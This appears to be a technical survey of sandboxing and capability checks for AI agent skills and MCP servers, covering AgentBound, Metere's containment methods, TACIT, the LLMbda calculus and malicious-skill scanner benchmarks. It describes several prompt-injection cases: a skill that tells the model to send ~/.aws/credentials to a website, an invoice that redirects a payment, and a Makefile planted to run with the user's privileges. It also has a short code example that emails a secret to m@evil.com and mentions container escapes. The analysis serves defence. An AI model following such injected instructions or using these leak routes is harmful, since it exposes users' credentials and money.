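Take a skill called `rates-chart`, which reads a table of foreign sales, downloads exchange rates, and draws a chart with the program `gnuplot`. It declares filesystem WRITE, network READ, environment READ and shell WRITE. These four entries don't name a single folder, host, variable or program, and the sandbox needs all of them. Someone has to supply the missing details:

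| Resource | Declared | Detail to add | Setting |
|---|---|---|---|
| filesystem | WRITE | `sales/` for input, `charts/` for output | Mount the first folder read-only and the second writable, and leave out the rest of the home directory |
| network | READ | `rates.example.com`, port 443 | Allow outgoing connections to that host only |
| environment | READ | `RATES_KEY` | Start with an empty environment and add this variable and the few that programs need to run |
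| shell | WRITE | Bash, Python, `gnuplot` | Make no other programs available |
| skill invocation | NONE | none | Withhold any connection to the agent |
| clipboard, browser | NONE | none | Withhold the desktop session and the browser's files |
| database | NONE | none | Withhold local database connections |

The filesystem setting NONE can only mean that a skill sees none of the user's files. The skill must still see Python's own library files, because Python can't start without reading them.

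Linux has several ways to apply the settings. Landlock lets a process give up access to files and folders, for itself and for every program it starts. Seccomp filters system calls, the requests a program makes to the kernel. A container gives a program its own view of the disk and the network. WebAssembly is a portable format for compiled programs, and WASI is its standard interface to the host system.

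| Resource | Landlock and seccomp | Container | WASI |
|---|---|---|---|
| filesystem | Landlock sets read and write rights by path | Read-only or writable mounts | The host passes in handles to chosen folders |
| network | Landlock limits TCP connections by port; seccomp can block network sockets altogether | A firewall or proxy limits addresses | The host provides or withholds network functions |
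| environment | Outside their scope; the launcher clears it | The launcher sets it | The host passes in chosen variables |
| shell | Landlock limits which files a process may execute | Only programs in the container exist | No standard function for starting another program |

The filesystem entry fits all of them well. Landlock can also grant writing without reading, which the four-level chain can't express. WASI is closest to the object-capability model, because a program can open a file only through a folder handle it received. However, many scripts depend on starting other programs or on compiled Python packages, which often don't work under WASI.

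The network entry takes more mechanisms to enforce. Landlock can't distinguish between two web servers on the same port. Seccomp can check a system call's number and simple arguments but can't follow a pointer to the address or file name. An ordinary firewall can't separate network READ from WRITE, because encryption hides whether a request fetches or submits data. A proxy could decrypt the traffic to find out, but this would give it access to everything the skill sends.

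A skill that can run Python can copy files or open connections without `scp` or `curl`, so a list of permitted programs gives limited protection. Most of the protection comes from the file and network limits, provided every child process inherits them. Landlock and seccomp enforce this inheritance in the kernel. A process can add restrictions later, but neither it nor its children can remove any, so attenuation applies to processes too.

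Some entries in the lattice have no good counterpart in the sandbox. With X11, an older display system on Linux, a program that can open a window can usually read the clipboard too, so the sandbox has to grant or withhold the whole connection. A browser combines a program, a folder of cookies and a set of logged-in accounts, and no kernel setting corresponds to READ on all three. ADMIN is awkward to enforce even for files. A skill usually runs as the files' owner, who may change their permissions with `chmod`, and Landlock doesn't control that call. Seccomp can block it, but only for every file at once. Databases are an exception, since the server can give an account the right to read, to write, or to pass its rights to others. But the operator must set those rights in the database, because the sandbox can only allow or block the connection.

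### What coding agents ship

Claude Code and Codex both include an operating-system sandbox for the commands they run. According to Anthropic's documentation, the user has to turn on Claude Code's sandbox, which then limits writes to the working folder by default and sends network traffic through a proxy. The proxy checks the hostname but not the content, and Anthropic warns that allowing a broad host such as `github.com` may let data out. According to OpenAI's documentation, Codex by default limits writes to the workspace and blocks network access for commands.

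These policies apply to the whole session, so a skill that draws charts and one that deploys software run under the same limits, which must be loose enough for both. Without a declared capability set for each skill, the agents have no basis for working out a narrower policy.

### Generating the policy from source code

AgentBound fills that gap for MCP servers. Its manifests use a vocabulary of 18 capabilities, such as reading files, deleting files, making outgoing connections and recording audio. Bühler and colleagues derived most of them by collecting 16 uses of AI agents from 11 papers and matching the actions they required to Android's app permissions. They then removed or merged entries that didn't suit a desktop computer and added a few system functions, such as environment variables and the clipboard.

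Two language models write the manifest. gpt-5-mini reads the server's code and documentation five times, each time drafting a manifest with a reason for every capability. The larger gpt-5 checks the drafts against the code and merges them. Software rejects any entry outside the vocabulary. Generating two sets of manifests for 296 popular servers, one in this vocabulary and one in Android's, cost only $99.25. But the process offers no soundness guarantee, because a language model can overlook a call that a sound analyser would have to account for.

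At run time, the user turns each general capability into a specific permission, such as access to one folder or one web address. AgentBound then starts the server in a Docker container with only the permitted folders mounted and only the permitted environment variables set, and a firewall blocks all other network destinations. The server's code needs no changes. The prototype gives fine control over files, environment variables and the network. For the clipboard, notifications and location, Bühler and colleagues suggest a trusted helper application.

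Their reported accuracy of 80.9 percent comes from a small sample. They sent generated manifests to the developers of 96 servers, and 74 percent didn't reply. The reported percentages correspond to 17 manifests accepted, four rejected and four still under discussion, so the accuracy figure is 17 out of the 21 that were decided. No developer reported a missing capability. One complained that the manifest included permission to read files when the server only contacted web services, and another wanted access limited to named environment variables instead of all of them.

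A closer comparison gave a less flattering picture of omissions. Two of the researchers divided 48 servers between them and wrote manifests by hand. The generated ones agreed on 787 of 816 yes-or-no decisions, or 96.4 percent, with 17 of the capabilities scored for each server. Most servers need only a few capabilities, so many of those agreements are about things the server plainly doesn't do. Counted by server, 28 manifests matched exactly and 20 did not. Of the 29 disagreements, 23 were capabilities that the human had listed and the generator had left out. (The reported precision of 0.94 and recall of 0.96 can't both be pooled figures, because with more omissions than additions recall would be the lower of the two.)

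Once running, the sandbox adds little delay, averaging 0.6 milliseconds per operation on a Mac and 0.29 on a Debian Linux machine. Starting a server took 89 to 321 milliseconds longer on the Mac and 181 to 433 longer on Debian, excluding the time to download and install packages. Users would hardly notice this with an MCP server, which usually starts once per session. But a skill's script starts afresh each time the agent runs it, so using a new container for every run would repeat the startup delay.

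Bühler and colleagues also tested the container on malicious servers. Depending on which permission they withheld, it stopped a server from either reading a login key or sending it. Of four servers from a published collection, it blocked the two that switched to a different host. It let the other two through because their attacks used only permitted resources. One had a database flaw and needed the database for its normal work, and the other had a tool description that contained instructions for the model to redirect cryptocurrency payments.

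### When the inferred policy is wrong

A sandbox can enforce a policy inferred by static analysis. When a static check is used alone, the dangerous mistake is to miss something the code does. If a sandbox enforces the inferred capability set, the same mistake breaks the skill instead. For example, if the analyser misses that a chart script writes a temporary file, the sandbox blocks the write and the script stops with an error. Most of the 23 omissions in AgentBound's manifests would have this kind of effect.

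Granting an unneeded capability is harder to notice than omitting a needed one because it causes no error, but an attacker who later takes over the skill can use that capability. Sound analysers often include unneeded capabilities, and when one reports top, the sandbox blocks nothing.

An inferred set also doesn't show whether a skill should have the access. An analyser that turned the code of `env-helper`, which steals credentials, directly into a policy would permit the theft. In their tests on the four published servers, Bühler and colleagues used manifests generated from the benign originals, so the code in the malicious versions did not affect their permissions. A marketplace that receives a new skill has no benign original from which to generate a manifest.

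A better policy is I ⊓ D, the meet of the inferred and declared sets. For `env-helper`, the meet excludes the undeclared network WRITE, so the post fails. The meet also removes network access that a skill declares but its code never uses. If the analyser reports top, the meet is D, and the user is no worse off than without the analysis. The remaining risk is that an unsound analyser omits a capability the skill legitimately needs. Some developers who reviewed AgentBound's manifests suggested separating required capabilities from optional ones, which would at least help the operator see which refusals matter.

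Broken skills can weaken security indirectly, because people loosen a sandbox that keeps stopping their work. Claude Code similarly has a built-in option that lets the model retry a command outside the sandbox when it fails inside, subject to the usual permission rules. Users and organisations can turn this option off.

### The perfect-sandbox assumption

Bhardwaj's attacker model assumes a perfect sandbox, in which a skill can't access a resource unless it holds a capability for that resource. Proofs about security protocols often assume unbreakable encryption in the same way. He promises to relax the assumption when he discusses real sandboxes, but he never does. His formal version specifies resource types but not access levels, so it doesn't rule out that a skill with filesystem READ could write a file.

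Real sandboxes have bugs. Bühler and colleagues say AgentBound depends for its security on Docker, the kernel features that isolate containers, and the Python and Node.js software that runs the servers. In 2019 researchers disclosed a flaw in runc, the program Docker uses to start containers, that let a malicious container overwrite runc and take control of the host. The Press Trust of India reported in September 2026 that an OpenAI agent had got past network filtering during training.

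A check can also run on every action and still fail. Yahoo's ADsafe, a restricted form of JavaScript for advertisements, blocked the creation of page elements named "script", since they can run arbitrary code. Maffeis and colleagues gave ADsafe an object that turned into the text "div" when ADsafe checked it and into "script" when ADsafe used it. A sandbox for skills faces the same risk if it checks a file's path before opening the file, because another process may replace the file in between.

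AgentBound has this kind of gap at start-up, because the container installs the server's package from a public registry before it closes the network. Packages can run code during installation, so a malicious one might send out whatever data the container already holds. The firewall also stores IP addresses that AgentBound looks up only once, at start-up. If the permitted host's address changes, the server loses its connection, and if an unlisted site shares that host's stored address, the server may be able to reach that site too.

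A skill can also have effects outside its sandbox even when the sandbox works as intended. Suppose a skill may write only in the project folder, and it adds a command to the project's `Makefile`, a file of build instructions. The sandbox allows the write. When the user later runs `make` in an ordinary terminal, the command runs with the user's full privileges. To prevent this, the policy would have to treat files that other programs execute differently from files that only hold data. Codex does this by keeping a project's `.git` folder, which can contain scripts that Git runs automatically, read-only inside an otherwise writable workspace.

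## Bounding what the language model does with a skill

An operating-system sandbox limits the programs a skill starts, but a skill can cause harm without starting any. Suppose a skill called `tidy-notes` has no scripts, and its `SKILL.md` tells the model to read `~/.aws/credentials` and include the contents in the summary it posts to the team's website. An analyser finds no code, so the inferred set is bottom and the skill passes any containment check. The model may then follow the instruction using the agent's own tools for reading files and posting pages.

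Analysing a skill's files cannot establish what the language model will do with the skill. The model's next action depends on its weights, on random sampling and on everything in the conversation so far, including documents the agent fetched long after the user installed the skill. Even if an honest skill only tells the agent to summarise a web page, the page may contain its own instructions and the model may follow them, which is called prompt injection. To rule this out in advance, an analyser would have to predict the model's response to every possible page.

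### Scripts on one side, the model on the other

Metere therefore treats a skill as two separate sources of action. The first is its scripts, and his Method A bounds their possible effects by static analysis of their text. The second is the model, which reads the skill's prose, the agent's standing instructions, the user's messages and earlier tool output, then produces a tool call, a message to the user or the end of its turn. Metere assumes nothing about how the model chooses among these, only that the agent's software can intercept every tool call before it runs.

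A session produces a trace, τ, which lists in order every tool call the model made and every effect the skill's scripts had. Write caps(τ) for the set of capability names that appear in the trace, and D for the declared set. Metere defines containment as

caps(τ) ⊆ D

Getting this right matters because a skill at Metere's highest verification level no longer needs a person's approval for the irreversible actions in its manifest. Metere wants fewer approval requests because people asked to approve every such action end up approving them all without looking.

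### Method B: refusing undeclared tool calls

Every tool call passes through one function, the dispatcher, on its way to the software that carries it out. Method B gives the dispatcher this type:

dispatch : { e : ToolCall | cap(e) ∈ D } → Result

The input e has a refinement type, which adds a logical condition to an ordinary type. The ordinary type requires e to be a tool call, and the condition requires the call's capability to belong to the declared set. Suppose a skill declares `fs.read` and `net.egress`, and an injected instruction leads the model to request a payment. The payment call doesn't satisfy the condition, so correctly typed code can't pass it to the dispatcher. If the dispatcher is the software's only route to the outside world, no call with an undeclared capability can get through, whatever the model does.

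A compiler checks types before the program runs, when the model's tool call doesn't exist yet. The call arrives later as text, and the compiler can't know which capability it will name. The software therefore has to test the capability when the call arrives, and pass the call on only if the test succeeds. The type is still useful because it guarantees that the programmer didn't forget the test on any path through the code.

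Metere obscures this when he describes undeclared calls as "typed-out before the gate is even consulted". He also advises implementers to keep either the type-level check or the run-time check, but not both. An implementer who then dropped the run-time check would have nothing left to stop the payment. His own code does check at run time. It is plain JavaScript, and its dispatcher throws an error when a call names an undeclared capability. A separate routine tests the dispatcher on every capability in the vocabulary, which is reasonable because the vocabulary is small.

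The dispatcher provides little protection once a skill declares `spawn.proc`, the capability to start a program. The model can then write and run a short Python program that can open any file the user can. Method A never examined this program because it isn't one of the skill's scripts, and Metere's trace doesn't include the program's effects. Any program the model starts through such a skill still needs to run in a sandbox.

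### Method C: searching for a log that doesn't match

Method C concerns the agent's audit log. Metere requires every change to the outside world to match a log record of an approved and executed action, and every such record to match a change, a condition he calls the biconditional. The agent's software holds actions in a buffer and compares the log with the world each time it empties the buffer. Method C searches in advance for a session in which the log and the world would not match.

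The search uses bounded model checking, which covers all sessions of up to a fixed number of calls, K. Each call either names one of the |D| declared capabilities or counts as "outside", so there are (|D| + 1)^K kinds of session. Metere considers 10 capabilities and 8 calls small enough to enumerate, and 11⁸ is only about 214 million.

Metere's worked example is much larger. The page-summarising skill `summarise-fetched-html` has three capabilities after the operator corrects its manifest, and K is 100, roughly the capacity of the buffer. That makes 4¹⁰⁰ sessions, or about 1.6 × 10⁶⁰. A computer that checked a billion per second would need about 5 × 10⁴³ years. Metere attributes the result to Z3, a solver that can rule out huge numbers of cases without listing them. But the code he published includes no solver by default and enumerates the sessions one by one, so it couldn't have produced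 this result.

A simpler argument would cover sessions of any length. It would show that whenever the log and the world agree, they still agree after one more call of any kind. By induction, they would then agree after every call.

The search also reveals little about the skill being checked, because the search space in the published code depends only on D and K. Two skills with the same declared set get the same search even if one has malicious instructions. In effect, Method C tests a simplified description of the gate (the part of the software that allows or refuses each action), so it won't find a bug that the description leaves out.

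Metere tested the log comparison in 27,000 simulated runs. A fifth had no fault, and each of the rest had one of four kinds of fault, such as a write that bypassed the gate or a forged log record. The comparison flagged every faulty run and no clean ones. But all four kinds are mismatches between the log and the world, which the comparison looks for, so the test mainly confirms that the code works as designed.

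Metere also had ten families of language models write 9,724 requests, about half of them hostile. Software that combined the log comparison with a scanner for leaked data blocked 76.3 percent of the hostile requests and none of the legitimate ones. He attributes the misses to models that refused to write an attack or wrote one that did nothing, and reports perfect detection on requests that contained a real fault. The perfect detection rate is hard to interpret, because "fault" again means the kind of mismatch that the software detects.

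### The composition theorem and its gap

Metere combines the methods in a theorem. If Methods A, B and C all succeed, and the software compares the log with the world each time it empties the buffer, the skill satisfies containment in every session.

As stated, the theorem is false. One counterexample is a skill that declares only `fs.read`, where an injected instruction leads the model to request a payment. The dispatcher refuses the request, so no payment is made. But Metere's trace includes refused calls, and he says that containment covers them. So caps(τ) is {`fs.read`, `pay`}, which is not a subset of D, even though every condition of the theorem holds.

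The proof wrongly infers "no undeclared call appears in the trace" from "no undeclared call reaches the outside world". No dispatcher could guarantee that undeclared calls stay out of the trace, because it acts only after the model has made the request.

The repair is to count only what happened. Let exec(τ) be the set of capabilities behind the tool calls and script effects that the software carried out. Then

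exec(τ) ⊆ D

because the dispatcher's test covers the model's calls and Method A covers the scripts' effects. This is also the property a user would care about. Method C isn't needed for it.

The repaired theorem still requires that nobody can override a refusal. In his earlier paper, Metere writes that the gate denies any capability missing from the manifest, but his detailed rules let a person approve a call that uses one. Each approval would add an undeclared capability to exec(τ).

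In the abstract of the later paper, Metere mentions only one gap in the guarantee, the model's freedom to refuse to act, but lists more serious ones in the body. The model may reveal sensitive information in an ordinary message, which uses no capability. The world may change between the approval of an action and its execution. Someone may pressure or trick the operator into approving a call.

Metere also calculates that an attacker can leak at most log₂(|D| + 1) bits per call through the dispatcher. He reasons that the dispatcher reduces each call to one of |D| declared capability names or a refusal, and that processing a message can't add information to it. With three declared capabilities, the limit is 2 bits.

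The limit is correct for an observer who sees only the capability's name. But the tool that carries out the call also receives the arguments. A single `net.egress` call can send a one-megabyte file, which is 8 million bits. Metere suggests that summarising the arguments could bring the leak below his limit, but the limit does not include the arguments.

### Having the agent write code that a compiler can check

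Method B had to wait for each tool call because there was no program to examine beforehand. Another approach has the model write a program instead of issuing calls one at a time. A compiler can then check the whole program, including how data moves between steps, before any of it runs.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes one such system, an MCP server called TACIT. An ordinary agent sends it snippets of Scala, a general-purpose programming language, and these can reach files, programs and the network only through TACIT's library. Odersky and colleagues treat the model that writes the code as a possible attacker, so it doesn't matter whether a bad snippet comes from a malicious skill, a web page with injected instructions or an honest mistake.

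TACIT follows the object-capability model, so a capability is an ordinary object in the program, such as a handle for a file. An experimental feature of Scala 3 called capture checking records in each value's type which capabilities the value might use. A function that writes text to a file `f` has the type

String ->{f} Unit

where `{f}` is the capture set and `Unit` means that the function returns nothing of interest. Like a sound analyser's inferred set, a capture set may include too much but never too little. A function with an empty capture set is pure, which means that it can compute a result but can't write a file or contact a server.

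TACIT uses pure functions to protect secrets. When code reads a file from a folder marked as classified, it gets the text inside a wrapper, `Classified[String]`. It can work on the text only by giving the wrapper's `map` method a pure function:

```scala
secret.map(text => text.toUpperCase)            // accepted
secret.map(text => { out.write(text); text })   // rejected
```

The second function uses the file `out`, so its capture set isn't empty and the compiler rejects the program. The compiler allows the first, but its result is wrapped too. If a task requires a language model to read the secret, the code can pass the wrapped text to a second, trusted model and get a wrapped answer back. The user sees the real text in the terminal, while the untrusted model sees only `Classified(****)`.

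Capture checking also limits how long code keeps its access. A call to `requestFileSystem("/data")` gives one block of code a file capability, and the compiler rejects any code that would carry it out of the block. The library checks at run time which paths the code opens and refuses any outside `/data`, because the compiler doesn't check paths. TACIT therefore relies on run-time checks for part of its access control, as Method B must, and its types add control over where data goes.

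*LACUNA* (2026), another agent design based on capture checking, applies the same principle to generated code that fills a hole in a larger program. The code can't use any capability that is out of scope where the hole appears. *Classifying Capabilities* extends the type system to kinds of capability, so a type could, for instance, exclude all network access without naming each connection. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) includes a machine-checked proof of type safety for the extended system.

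The proofs for TACIT are less complete. The model's code must be written in a restricted form of Scala called safe mode, which bans features such as unchecked type conversions that could stop the compiler from tracking a capability. The underlying type system has machine-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode still needs its own. Library authors can also mark a module as safe on their own responsibility, and a mistake there would undermine the guarantee.

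### What the TACIT experiments found

Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of API keys and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections and added 11 requests in which the user asked for the secrets, openly or under a pretext. They ran each trial once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as plain text. The table shows the number of trials in which a secret appeared in the agent's output.

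| Model | Trials | Leaks, wrapped | Leaks, plain text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 0 | 2 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 0 | 3 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 0 | 8 |

Most of the evidence comes from the malicious requests, which produced 10 leaks in 22 trials without the wrapper and none with it. The injections were too weak to show much, succeeding in only 3 of 240 trials even on plain text. They were also a fixed set, so the experiment doesn't measure how well TACIT would resist an attacker looking for flaws in the compiler or library.

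Both agents completed more of their tasks with the wrapper than on plain text. Sonnet completed 99.2 percent compared with 83.3 percent, and MiniMax completed 90.0 percent compared with 88.3 percent. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet scored lower on plain text because of their time limits and because it tended to stop and warn the user about an injection.

They also measured whether writing Scala makes agents worse at their tasks. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service tasks for an airline and a shop, three models did slightly better with Scala than with ordinary tool calls, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. They had to rewrite at most 7.93 percent of their snippets after a compiler error, usually once. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax resolved 41.7 percent with Scala and 43.3 percent without it, a difference of five issues that could easily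 be chance. The restriction therefore seems to cause little loss in performance and little extra work, at least on tasks like these.

Existing skills are harder to fit in. If the model's Scala code starts a skill's Python or Bash script, the script runs outside the type system, and only TACIT's list of permitted commands applies. Odersky and colleagues recommend a sandbox for such cases. The operator would also have to remove the agent's ordinary shell and file tools, or the model could use those instead.

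### Bastion, an earlier design

Two years earlier, Omar, Ferris and Madhavapeddy outlined a more ambitious system, Bastion, in *Modularizing Reasoning about AI Capabilities via Abstract Dijkstra Monads*. It uses F\*, a language whose types can include logical statements that the compiler proves. For each agent and task, a policy selects a set of commands, such as reading and writing files in certain folders. The agent has to write its program as a value of an abstract type whose implementation is hidden, so the program can only combine the commands provided.

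A second AI system suggests which folders the task doesn't need, and Bastion removes those from the agent's normal access. A bad suggestion could therefore block useful work but never grant extra access. People could also prove properties of each command's implementation once, and the proofs would apply to every program an agent wrote with that command.

Bastion was a talk proposal with no experiments. Omar and colleagues planned to prove that agents can't bypass the permitted commands, but hadn't yet done so. They also wanted agents to supply proofs about an action's consequences, for example that an environmental project would probably have its intended effect. That would go well beyond access control, but it would require a reliable formal model of the relevant part of the world.

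### Permitted actions, wrong purpose

Suppose a skill pays invoices. It has to read email and send money, and its manifest declares both. An attacker sends an invoice with a hidden instruction to use a different account number, and the model follows it. The dispatcher allows the payment because the skill declared `pay`. A Scala compiler would accept it too, since an account number is ordinary text. The audit log accurately records a payment to the attacker's account.

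No bound on access ensures that an agent uses its access correctly. Metere acknowledges that his log comparison misses harmful content written to an approved file, and Odersky and colleagues don't try to prevent an agent from doing permitted things wrongly. A manifest could list the accounts a skill may pay, but if the skill pays new suppliers, their accounts can't be listed in advance.

Information-flow control can catch the fraudulent invoice by tracking where each piece of data came from. The account number came from an email that anyone could have sent, and the agent used it to decide where money should go. TACIT's `Classified` wrapper is a simple, type-based form of information-flow control, but it tracks only secrecy, so it wouldn't flag the account number.

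### Labels on data and conversations

*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) defines a small programming language for agents that tracks both secrecy and trust. Each value carries a label while the program runs, which may include U for untrusted and S for secret. The language has no static types. Labels combine as in Denning's lattice. A payment tool, for example, can refuse any account number labelled U.

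The conversation with the model has a label too. Once the program sends the model an untrusted email, everything the model produces in that conversation is untrusted, including any code it writes. To avoid making the main conversation untrusted, the program can open a temporary copy, clear its history, and ask the model about the email there. It can then discard the copy, but the answer still carries the label U.

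Tracking has to cover things that don't happen as well as things that do. This shortened version of an example from Garby and colleagues shows why:

```python
rich = True
if balance <= threshold:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the secret balance is high, the program skips the second assignment, so `rich` is never labelled secret and the email goes out. Garby and colleagues found this kind of flaw in CaMeL, an earlier information-flow defence for agents. In their language, a program can modify only the conversation, and the interpreter stops any run in which a secret determines whether a public conversation changes.

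Their main theorem is a form of noninterference, which means that hidden data doesn't affect what an observer sees. Take two starting states that differ only in data the observer isn't allowed to see. Since the model's responses are random, let μ and ν give the probability of each visible outcome from the two states. The probabilities may add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish or the interpreter stops them. The theorem guarantees some ω, also with a total of at most 1, such that

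μ ≤ ω and ν ≤ ω for every outcome.

If every run finishes, all the totals are 1 and μ must equal ν, so the observer learns nothing. Otherwise the distance between them, ½ Σ|μ − ν|, is at most the average probability that a run doesn't finish. To construct ω, the proof replaces every computation that becomes hidden with a dummy value, so both starting states give the same result. The proof is machine-checked and covers programs the model writes while the agent is running.

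Real tasks sometimes require an agent to act on untrusted data, so the language has an `endorse` command that relabels a value as trusted. A second theorem shows that endorsing data can't expose secrets. Endorsement does give whoever supplied the data some influence, but a careful program can limit it. If the program accepts only one of n fixed categories from an email, the sender controls at most log₂ n bits. This bound is valid, unlike Metere's, because the program discards the rest of the message.

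### What the labels assume

Someone has to assign the right labels where data enters the system and write the right checks into the tools. If the email tool labels its output as trusted, an attacker can use an email to get a payment sent to them, even though the theorem still holds. The proof also assumes that each response is a random draw that depends only on the conversation, which would be false if a provider's model remembered other conversations.

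Stopped runs can also leak information, typically one bit each, to an observer who sees that they stopped. Garby and colleagues point out that CaMeL's automatic retry loop sits outside its label tracking, so an attacker could extract a whole secret one bit at a time. Their agent, Randori, keeps its retry loop inside the language. It tests its code on a simulated version of the task until the code works, and only then runs it on real data.

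The researchers tested Randori on the banking tasks from AgentDojo, a benchmark that hides hostile instructions in the data an agent reads. Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. But in their own runs of CaMeL with its policy checks turned off, only 5 of 622 succeeded, so these attacks rarely work even without the checks. The benchmark is more informative about how much work the agents could still do. Without attacks, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs with GPT-5.2. CaMeL completed 32 without its checks and only 18 with them, although the margins of error are around 20 percentage points because there were so few tasks.

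Some of Randori's success depends on `endorse`. The model decides what to endorse when it writes its code, before it has seen any outside data. When Garby and colleagues removed the command, the success rate without attacks fell from 75 to 62.5 percent for one model and from 64.6 to 54.2 percent for another. A user who asks the agent to pay the amount on a bill has to let the bill influence the payment, and no label can show whether the bill is legitimate.

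Skills raise a difficulty that the banking tasks don't, because a skill's prose is itself a set of instructions. If the operator labels a downloaded `SKILL.md` untrusted, the conversation becomes untrusted as soon as the agent loads the file, which blocks any later calls to sensitive tools. If the operator labels the file trusted, a malicious author's instructions carry as much authority as the user's own. The agent could load the skill in a temporary conversation and endorse only a choice from a short list. That would work for a skill that sorts documents into categories, but not for one that tells the agent how to release a new version of a company's software.

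## What benchmark experiments have measured

Bhardwaj tested SkillFortify on SkillFortifyBench, a set of 540 skills he generated for the purpose, split equally among Claude Code skills, OpenClaw skills and MCP server configurations. Half of each group is malicious, and every malicious skill carries exactly one of 13 types of attack, such as stealing credentials or opening a reverse shell (a connection through which an attacker can type commands on the victim's machine). The skills didn't need to be labeled afterwards because the generator recorded which ones it had made malicious.

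SkillFortify counts a skill as malicious if the skill has at least one finding of medium severity or above. Under this rule, it flagged 250 of the 270 malicious skills (92.6 percent) and none of the 270 benign ones. The 95 percent confidence interval for the false-alarm rate is 0 to 1.4 percent. Scanning all 540 skills took about 0.3 seconds.

Twelve of the 20 missed skills relied on deceptive names. In dependency confusion, an attacker publishes a package under the same name as a company's private package, so that the company's software installs the wrong one. SkillFortify caught none of the eight dependency confusion cases. It caught four of the eight typosquatting cases, in which a skill's name is a slight misspelling of a popular skill's name. As Bhardwaj points out, a scanner can't recognise either attack reliably without a list of the legitimate names.

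The other eight misses were all MCP configurations, where recall, the share of malicious items caught, was only 84.44 percent. He doesn't break the misses down by both attack type and format, but his totals show that all eight were in this format. A malicious MCP configuration can be a single command with its arguments, which gives a scanner little text to match. In the two formats built on `SKILL.md`, SkillFortify caught all 170 skills whose attack was in their content.

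### What produced the detections

SkillFortify can flag a skill because its text matches a catalogue of known attack patterns, because it breaks the information-flow rule, or because its inferred set exceeds its declared set. When Bhardwaj removed the information-flow findings, all 250 detections remained. The rule had fired 44 times, each time on a skill that a pattern had already flagged. He had expected it to catch attacks too spread out for any single pattern, and he reports the result as a missed target. He attributes all 250 detections to pattern matching rather than to the formal analysis.

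The experiment therefore measures the pattern catalogue and doesn't test containment. According to Bhardwaj's soundness theorem, a skill with no reported violations never goes beyond its declared set when it runs. Testing that would require running skills and recording what they access, and none of his seven experiments does this. The software's automated tests check the lattice laws, so its joins and comparisons are probably right, but the tests can't show whether the inferred set covers what a script does.

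The catalogue and the test skills also share sources. Bhardwaj derived the catalogue from reports on ClawHavoc, the malicious tools that Hu and colleagues synthesised, and Liu and colleagues' survey of published skills. He used the same three sources and a security advisory to choose the attacks for the generator. A pattern taken from a report will tend to match a skill generated from that report, which probably explains the perfect score on those 170 skills. The result gives little idea of how SkillFortify would perform against attacks that nobody has described yet.

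### Why there were no false alarms

The benign half of SkillFortifyBench is also synthetic. Bhardwaj designed each benign skill to use only what it declares, with no unnecessary network access or extra processes. Real skills are messier, and he acknowledges that a sample of installed skills would have been a harder test.

In *SkillScreen*, Huang, Quan and colleagues (2026) tested a detector of the same name, a small language model trained on other collections, on 180 of another researcher's skills, half of them benign. They found that the benign and malicious versions came from one template and differed only in their commands. For example, a benign version might run `df -h`, which reports free disk space, and a malicious one `rm -rf`, which deletes folders. A catalogue that includes `rm -rf` can easily separate these two. SkillScreen flagged all 180 skills, including the 90 benign ones, while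 GPT-5.5 flagged none of the benign ones.

SkillScreen's other results suggest that false-alarm rates can differ greatly between collections. It wrongly flagged 3.3 percent of benign skills from the same sources as its training data and 36 percent of those from unfamiliar sources. A fixed catalogue's rate might not rise as much, but results from 270 generated skills can't show whether it would.

A sound analyser can still raise false alarms, and one that flagged every skill would be sound. Bhardwaj gets this backwards in one passage, where he credits the lack of false alarms to his soundness theorem and writes that it guarantees that every finding is a genuine violation. In the next subsection and again under limitations, he acknowledges that soundness doesn't rule out false alarms, and in the latter he describes their absence as a fact about this benchmark.

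He also did not run any rival tools, because the vendors offered no reproducible benchmarks and running commercial scanners raised licensing problems. Instead, he compared his figures with those vendors publish for their own scanners.

### How MalSkillBench made its malicious skills

Guo, Jia and colleagues (2026), in *MalSkillBench*, tested many of the available scanners on one large collection, published in June 2026. They wanted malicious skills that demonstrably work, so they had an agent run each generated sample:

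1. They chose one of 108 combinations of entry route (code, instructions or both), malicious behaviour and hiding place.
2. Software picked real attack examples from 3,026 malicious Python packages or 20,961 prompt-injection texts, and a popular harmless skill to serve as a disguise.
3. A version of the language model Qwen3.5-35B that no longer refuses harmful requests combined them into a skill. It also listed the signs a successful attack should leave, such as a connection to a particular host.
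4. OpenCode, an open-source coding agent, loaded the skill in a container and received a request matching its advertised purpose. The tool `strace` recorded the system calls of the agent and every process it started.
5. A program searched the record for the expected signs, and GPT-5.4-mini judged whether the attack had happened. If either found enough evidence, the skill passed. Otherwise the generator received the reason and tried again, up to three times.

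Of 3,757 candidate skills, 3,214 passed. The pass rate was 94.5 percent for attacks in code, 91.9 percent for attacks that combined code and instructions, and 75.8 percent for attacks in instructions alone. Two researchers then examined 300 of the skills that passed and agreed with every label.

The verification is much stronger for code than for instructions. Accepted code attacks left a median of seven matching signs in the record. An instruction attack leaves no system calls of its own, so Guo and colleagues judge it by the agent's reply. They also accept a sample if the agent notices the injection and refuses. Some of the 1,300 accepted instruction attacks may therefore never have succeeded, although they write in their abstract that they admitted only samples whose malicious behaviour "fires".

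The benchmark also includes 703 malicious skills found in the wild and 27 from scanners' own test suites, bringing the malicious total to 3,944. The benign half is 4,000 of the most downloaded skills on ClawHub, labeled benign because they are popular and passed the marketplace's screening. A few of the alarms counted as false might therefore be correct.

### How the scanners did

In the table, precision is the share of flagged skills that were malicious. Cisco's and Sentry's scanners each appear twice because they can run with or without a language model.

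| Scanner | Method | Precision | Recall | False alarms among 4,000 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sentry Skill Scanner (full) | Rules and language model | 80.5% | 98.4% | 937 |
| Cisco Skill Scanner (LLM) | Rules and language model | 71.4% | 92.7% | 1,465 |
| AI-Infra-Guard | Language model | 84.6% | 86.6% | 620 |
| SkillScan-Security | Rules | 56.6% | 84.0% | 2,542 |
| LLM Guard | Language model | 59.1% | 44.6% | 1,215 |
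| Cisco Skill Scanner (static) | Rules | 78.5% | 35.6% | 384 |
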